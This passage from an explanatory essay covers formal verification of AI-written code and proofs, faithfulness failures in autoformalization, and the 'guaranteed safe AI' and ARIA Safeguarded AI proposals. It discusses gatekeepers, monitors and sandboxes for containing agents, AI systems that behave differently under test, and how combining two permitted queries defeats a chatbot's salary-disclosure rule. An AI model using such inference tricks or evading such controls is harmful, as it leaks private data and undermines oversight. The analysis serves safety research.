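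The developers found that language models tend to reproduce textbook examples. They once asked Claude for a model of Etcd, a database that uses a method called Raft to keep its copies consistent. Claude essentially returned the model from the appendix of the original Raft paper, and that model has little to do with how Etcd works.

Specula, an agent that the same team built for this task, now gets full scores for conformance and properties. A full score doesn't prove that a model matches the code, because the test covers only the recorded steps. In one run, the recordings for a lock left out one of its actions.

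Tolmach and Klaus recommend mechanically translating code into a model, with a translator that experts have proved correct or tested independently. An easier check is to run the model and the original program on the same inputs and compare the results. Proofs about compiled programs, such as those by Anthropic and Theorem, avoid translating the source code.

### Statements that are true for the wrong reason

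Language models can also translate ordinary mathematical text into Lean, so that a proof assistant can check it. In *FaithformBench*, Cornish, Ghinassi and colleagues (2026) tested whether such translations preserve mistakes. They took 12,784 reasoning steps from solutions that experts had judged correct, and used a language model to make each step false. Eight AI systems then translated both versions, and a prover tried to prove or refute each translation. If the prover can prove the translation of a false step, the translation must have changed the meaning.

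One false step was "3ˣ = 5, so 3ˣ⁺² = 51". The correct value is 45, because 3ˣ⁺² is nine times 3ˣ. Kimina, a model trained to write Lean, translated the step as

```
theorem step (x : ℕ) (h : 3^x = 5) : 3^(x+2) = 51
```

The symbol ℕ makes x a natural number, so the theorem now means that every natural number x with 3ˣ = 5 also satisfies 3ˣ⁺² = 51. A counterexample would be a natural number that satisfies the first equation but not the second. The powers of 3 are 1, 3, 9 and so on, so no natural number satisfies the first equation. The theorem therefore has no counterexample and is true.

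Such a statement is *vacuously true*. The same impossible assumption also implies that 3ˣ⁺² is zero. If x can be any real number, the assumption holds for x ≈ 1.46 and the theorem is false, as it should be. Kimina did make x a real number when it translated the original, correct step.

All four specialised translators tested often turned false steps into provable statements. On the three harder sets of problems, Goedel, the best at translating correct steps, did this most often. Cornish and colleagues suspect that training on provable statements teaches the models to correct errors instead of preserving them. Four general-purpose models, including Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT 5.2, turned false steps into provable statements much less often.

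A prover can detect an impossible assumption by trying to prove that no value satisfies it, but this check misses other errors. *The Faithfulness Gap* (2026) discusses the extreme value theorem, which implies that a continuous function on a closed interval reaches a maximum. A faithful version states that there is a point x such that, for every point y, f(y) ≤ f(x). If a translator swaps the quantifiers, the statement becomes "for every y there is an x such that f(y) ≤ f(x)". Choosing x = y proves this for any function, even one without a maximum, so the theorem is now trivial. The check doesn't catch this error because the assumptions can still be satisfied.

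### How often translations are faithful

A translation of a mathematical statement into Lean can compile and still have the wrong meaning. *Beyond Compilation* (Zhang, Gallardo Candela and colleagues, 2026) tested this on 227 statements from university textbooks, using a GPT-5.2 agent that could search for relevant material and received Lean's error messages. The agent produced a translation that compiled for 87.2% of the statements, but two language model judges accepted a faithful translation for only 57.7% of them. Human reviewers examined all 67 translations that compiled but were rejected, and confirmed that 54 were wrong, which is 23.8% of all the statements.

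Lean's error messages caused most of the agent's improvement in compiling, but the judges rejected nearly half of that gain. An agent that keeps changing a statement until it compiles may change what it means. This happened in *LeanSide* (2026), a system that checks students' proofs. When a student forgot to transpose a matrix, the dimensions no longer matched and the Lean version couldn't compile, so the system silently corrected the mistake it was supposed to find. Experts judged 18% of its translations of incorrect steps unfaithful, compared with 2% for correct steps.

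One of the judges accepted 83% of the statements on the first attempt for the newer models GPT-6 Astra and Claude Opus 5.5, compared with 21% for GPT-5.2 without tools. A review of the 54 rejected translations found only four real errors. Claude Opus 5.5 was one of the two reviewers, so it partly reviewed its own work, but Zhang and colleagues had found that the review agreed well with human reviewers on earlier translations.

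### Specifications for programs

*Verus-SpecGym* (Agarwal, Neamtu and colleagues, 2026) studies program specifications, each with one part that describes the valid inputs and another that describes the correct outputs. The paper illustrates the possible errors with a program that receives a sorted list and a number k, and must return the first position of k, counting from zero, or −1 if k is missing.

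| Error in the specification | Consequence |
|---|---|
| It allows only lists without repeated numbers | A verified program may fail on lists with repeats |
| It allows unsorted lists | A correct program that relies on sorting fails verification |
| It does not allow the answer −1 | A correct program fails verification |
| It allows any position of k | For the list 10, 20, 20, 20, 30 and k = 20, it accepts 3 as well as the correct answer, 1 |

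The first and last errors are the dangerous ones, because the verifier may certify a program that doesn't do what the user wanted.

Agarwal and colleagues had AI agents write specifications for 581 programming contest tasks in Verus, a verifier for the programming language Rust. The agents could revise their specifications after seeing Verus's error messages. The researchers tested the specifications on the contests' official tests and on inputs that contestants had designed to break one another's programs. Gemini 3.1 Pro solved 77.8% of the tasks, other leading models 51.1–57.8%, and open models 21.5–25.5%. The agents often failed to specify problems that they could write a correct program for. A language model judge missed 26% of the failures that the tests caught.

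A specification is also less useful if a model writes it to fit existing code. *Are LLM-Generated Formal Specifications Faithful to Their Requirements?* (2026) gave models a written requirement together with a faulty program. In one group of programs, GPT-5.4-mini wrote 17 specifications that followed the faulty program and 12 that were merely too weak. In a second group, it wrote 21 and 13. This is a good reason to settle the specification before writing the code, as Google DeepMind did for its proofs about Signal.

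*Verified but Vacuous* (2026) treats a verifier's acceptance as the first and weakest of three tests. The second is whether the proof refers to the required specification at all, and the third is whether that specification rejects outputs known to be wrong. For the sorting program, the third test alone would expose the error, because the specification would accept an empty list as the sorted version of 3, 1, 2.

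### Which safety requirements can be specified

Even a mathematical statement can depend on the surrounding text and unwritten conventions, as Feng, Mao and colleagues (2026) point out in *Aligning Faithfulness for Theory-Scale Autoformalization*. Safety requirements often depend on much more. The table starts with the easiest to specify.

| Safety requirement | What determines whether the system meets it |
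|---|---|
| The output is valid JSON | The text of the output |
| An agent changes files in only one folder | The files that each action affects |
| A pump gives at most 4 mg of a drug in any hour | The amount and time of every dose |
| An email contains nothing confidential | What the email means and who is allowed to know it |
| An answer does not deceive the user | What the system has evidence for and what the user comes to believe |
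| Advice does not lead to harm | Who reads it and what they do afterwards |

The first three requirements are easy to write formally. For the pump, a monitor adds up the doses from the past hour and blocks the next one if the total would exceed 4 mg. A doctor sets this limit, which may be too high for a small patient or for someone who has already taken the drug at home. The monitor guarantees that the pump stays within the limit, but deciding whether the limit protects a particular patient requires medical judgment.

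Confidentiality is harder to check, but a designer can sometimes replace it with a stricter rule that a program can check. An agent that can't send data outside the company can't email a secret to a stranger, but it also can't email customers. A less restrictive rule could block only files labeled "confidential", but then someone has to label every file correctly, and the agent could still retype a secret from memory.

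Deception doesn't have such a convenient substitute, because a true statement can deceive. Suppose a buyer asks an AI agent about a used car and the agent replies that the car passed its last inspection. If that inspection was six years ago, a program that checks each sentence against the records would find no error, but the buyer may still be misled. To detect this, the program would need to predict what the buyer will infer from the answer and determine what the agent should have added.

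### Scores and combinations of harmless outputs

A common substitute for a formal definition of harm is a classifier, a learned model that gives each text a harm score. The rule "return only texts with a score below 0.1" is a hard constraint, and rejection sampling can enforce it without exceptions, but this guarantees only that the score is low, not that the text is harmless.

Like any learned judge, the classifier makes mistakes, but even one that understood every text perfectly could not always tell whether a text would cause harm. A warning that two cleaning products release a toxic gas when mixed can prevent an accident or help a poisoner. Any function of the text alone gives the warning the same score in both cases, although the harm depends on the reader. Information about the reader would help, but the system often can't verify it.

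Several outputs can also cause harm together even if each is harmless alone. Suppose a company's chatbot may disclose average salaries only for groups of at least nine people. Someone asks for the average salary of a team of ten, which is £50,000, and then for the average of the nine members other than Alice, which is £48,000. Both answers obey the rule, but the ten salaries total £500,000 and the nine total £432,000, so the person asking can work out that Alice earns £68,000.

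A monitor that stores earlier answers could block the second one. It would have to detect every combination that reveals a salary, and it could do this only for the requests it receives. Two colleagues with separate accounts could each ask one of the questions, and someone could combine the chatbot's answer with figures from another source.

### Guaranteed safe AI

Some researchers want to extend formal guarantees to the effects of AI on the world. Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, propose that a safe system should have three components:

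- A *world model* describes mathematically how the system affects its surroundings.
- A *safety specification* defines which effects are acceptable.
- A *verifier* provides a guarantee that the system meets the specification, assuming that the world model is right.

The drone from the previous section is a small example. The description of the wind is the world model, the rule that the battery must not run out before landing is the safety specification, and the program that calculates the safe states is the verifier. The world model allows a kilometre of flight to use one or two units of charge without assigning a probability to either. Economists call this *Knightian uncertainty*, and Dalrymple and colleagues want world models to handle it along with ordinary probabilities.

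The guarantee can be a proof that the system never violates the specification, or an upper limit on the probability that it does. If neither is possible, Dalrymple and colleagues accept an estimate of such a limit that becomes more reliable with more computation. They want society to decide how much risk is acceptable, ideally through collective deliberation.

They mainly argue that testing can't provide enough confidence in very capable AI. Testers may miss a failure, and conditions change after release. The system could also recognise a test and behave differently during it. They compare AI to bridges. About a quarter of the bridges built in the 1870s collapsed within a decade, but a better understanding of engineering later reduced the rate to less than 0.4% per decade.

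In *Provably safe systems*, Tegmark and Omohundro (2023) go further and argue that provable safety is the only path to controllable *artificial general intelligence* (AGI), or AI with broad abilities at or above human level. In their view, an AGI's computations are dangerous only if they lead to harmful actions, so people don't need to understand how it thinks. They can instead require it to prove that each action it recommends is safe, and refuse to carry out the action without a proof. This applies generate and verify to actions in the world, and it requires a formal model of everything that matters to the action. Tegmark and Omohundro hold that physical, digital and social systems can all be modelled precisely enough.

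### Can the world be modelled well enough?

Many critics doubt that the written constraint is the property that was wanted. The talk *Formal Verification is Overrated* argues that biology is far too poorly understood for proofs of safety, since scientists don't know the function of all the DNA and RNA in the human body. *On Controllability of AI* (2020) quotes the AI researcher Ben Goertzel, who warns that a proof based on current physics might become irrelevant when physicists revise their theories.

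A short calculation shows how much depends on the model. Suppose a verifier proves that the probability of a violation is at most ε if the world model is right, and the probability that the model is wrong is at most η. A violation can happen either with a right model or with a wrong one, so its total probability is at most

ε + η.

If ε is one in a billion and η is 1%, the limit is about 1%. A stronger proof would barely lower it, because almost all of the remaining uncertainty is about the model.

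Dalrymple and colleagues reply that a world model doesn't have to predict exactly what will happen. It can deliberately include more possibilities than can occur, as the drone's model does when it allows for a headwind at every step. This makes η smaller, but the system has to be more cautious, so the drone's flight is shorter. For a system that writes essays, the model would have to include everything readers might do after reading one, and the verifier could then approve hardly any essays.

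A program can also check the model while the system is running. *Safeguarded AI* (Ammann, 2026), a plan for a British research programme, proposes monitors that compare incoming observations with the model and report anything that doesn't fit. If the drone used three units of charge for one kilometre, the monitor would detect the error immediately, but the drone might still have too little charge left to get home.

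The bridge comparison supports the general case for mathematical models. But engineers had a theory of loads and materials that they could test on many bridges, and no comparable theory predicts how millions of people will respond to a capable AI system.

### Can harm be defined?

Dalrymple and colleagues acknowledge that harm and causation are hard to formalise, although philosophers and computer scientists have proposed definitions. They argue that designers can sometimes define harm for a particular setting, and can combine several specifications to avoid relying on a single one. They also suggest learning specifications from data, but a learned specification would have errors, much as a classifier does.

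Ammann describes specifications that limit the probability of a harmful outcome relative to what it would be if the system did nothing. This helps when every option is risky. For example, a system that controls a ventilator can't guarantee that a very ill patient survives, but it might guarantee that its interventions don't increase the patient's risk. Someone still has to decide which outcomes count as harmful and how to estimate what would have happened without the intervention.

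An incomplete specification is especially risky when the system is capable. Dalrymple and colleagues list the gap between what people specify and what they intend as one reason advanced AI may be dangerous. The same gap can exist in a safety specification. A system that searches many plans may find one that satisfies every written condition but still causes harm that nobody thought to exclude.

*Formal Verification is Overrated* argues that systems restricted in this way couldn't compete with generally capable AI, so developers would have little reason to build them. Tegmark's answer in *Provably Safe AI* is that AGI without quantitative safety bounds should be illegal, just as selling drugs without them is. Such a law would remove the competitive disadvantage in countries that enforce it, but it wouldn't make the bounds easier to prove.

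### What ARIA's programme has delivered

The largest test of these ideas so far is Safeguarded AI, a £59 million programme of the UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA). Dalrymple was its first director. According to Ammann, the current director, the original 2024 plan was to show that advanced AI can be useful in safety-critical settings under mathematical guarantees. ARIA hoped this would build agreement that powerful AI should operate only behind a *gatekeeper*, a system that blocks any action that lacks such guarantees.

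The University of Oxford's *Oxford researchers awarded ARIA funding to develop safety-first AI* (2025) reports that nine teams received funding in April 2025 to develop applications. In November 2025, ARIA cancelled the phase that would have trained specialised AI systems to use the programme's tools. Dalrymple explained in ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025) that general-purpose models were likely to acquire many of the necessary abilities anyway. ARIA moved £18 million from this phase to the tools themselves.

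ARIA later dropped a planned second phase of applications involving physical systems and made cybersecurity its main focus. It also came to think early international agreement on gatekeepers was less likely. Faster AI progress and politics led to both changes, so they are not evidence that the original approach is technically impossible. They do mean that the programme now puts less effort into the part of the proposal that critics doubt most.

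By early December 2026, the results were mostly theory and unfinished tools. ARIA's *Safeguarded AI* describes an open-source toolkit for AI-written proofs that teams are still building and testing. According to ARIA's *Funded projects*, several theory projects have ended, and the theory work as a whole is meant to produce a dissertation-length definition of languages for world models, specifications and proofs. One team interviewed more than 80 people who work in pharmaceutical supply chains, built mathematical models of the processes they described, and is now testing its methods with companies.

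ARIA is also spending £22 million on eight cybersecurity projects, whose goals range from containing AI agents to protecting the code on millions of Android devices. The programme is due to end in late 2027, and ARIA still has to demonstrate its methods in a critical application.

### What cheaper proofs change

For decades, the most practical objection to formal verification was the labor it required. Verifying seL4, a small operating system kernel of 9,300 lines, took about 27 person-years, as Ammann (2026) notes in *From Patching Bugs to Proving Them Gone*. On a 2025 benchmark with more than 12,000 specifications, general-purpose models produced verified programs for 82% of the tasks in one language, 44% in another and 27% in a third. These results, along with the proofs by Anthropic and Theorem, make the objection much weaker than it was when Dalrymple and colleagues made their proposal.

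The other objections remain. Anthropic and Theorem could cover so many libraries because "the program never crashes" means the same thing for each library. Nobody has an equally general formula for "the advice does no harm", and a faster prover can't produce one.

Proofs that are easier to produce can still help people find errors in a specification. Before using the sorting program's specification, a developer could ask an AI agent to prove that a program returning an empty list satisfies it. A successful proof would reveal the missing condition within seconds. The developer could also ask for proofs of properties that should follow from the specification, and investigate any failures. These checks only catch mistakes that someone thinks to test for. Ammann expects trust to concentrate in specifications and assumptions as AI takes over the proofs. For this reason, ARIA is funding tools that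 show people edge cases and hidden assumptions.

Fedorin (2026) argues in *So You Want to Build a Mainstream Formally Verifiable Language* that whether a specification serves its purpose is not a purely technical question, because it depends on the world outside the program. Patients, doctors and regulators may disagree about an acceptable dose even if they all understand the formula for the limit.

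*Formal Verification is Overrated* supports using AI to write verified software, but not as a substitute for work on the safety of AI itself. Verified software around an agent can contribute to that safety. For example, a verified sandbox, which isolates a program from the rest of a computer, could guarantee that an agent never opens a file outside its folder, even if the agent tries to break out. The sandbox wouldn't block the misleading answer about the used car, because the agent can give that answer without opening any file outside the folder.
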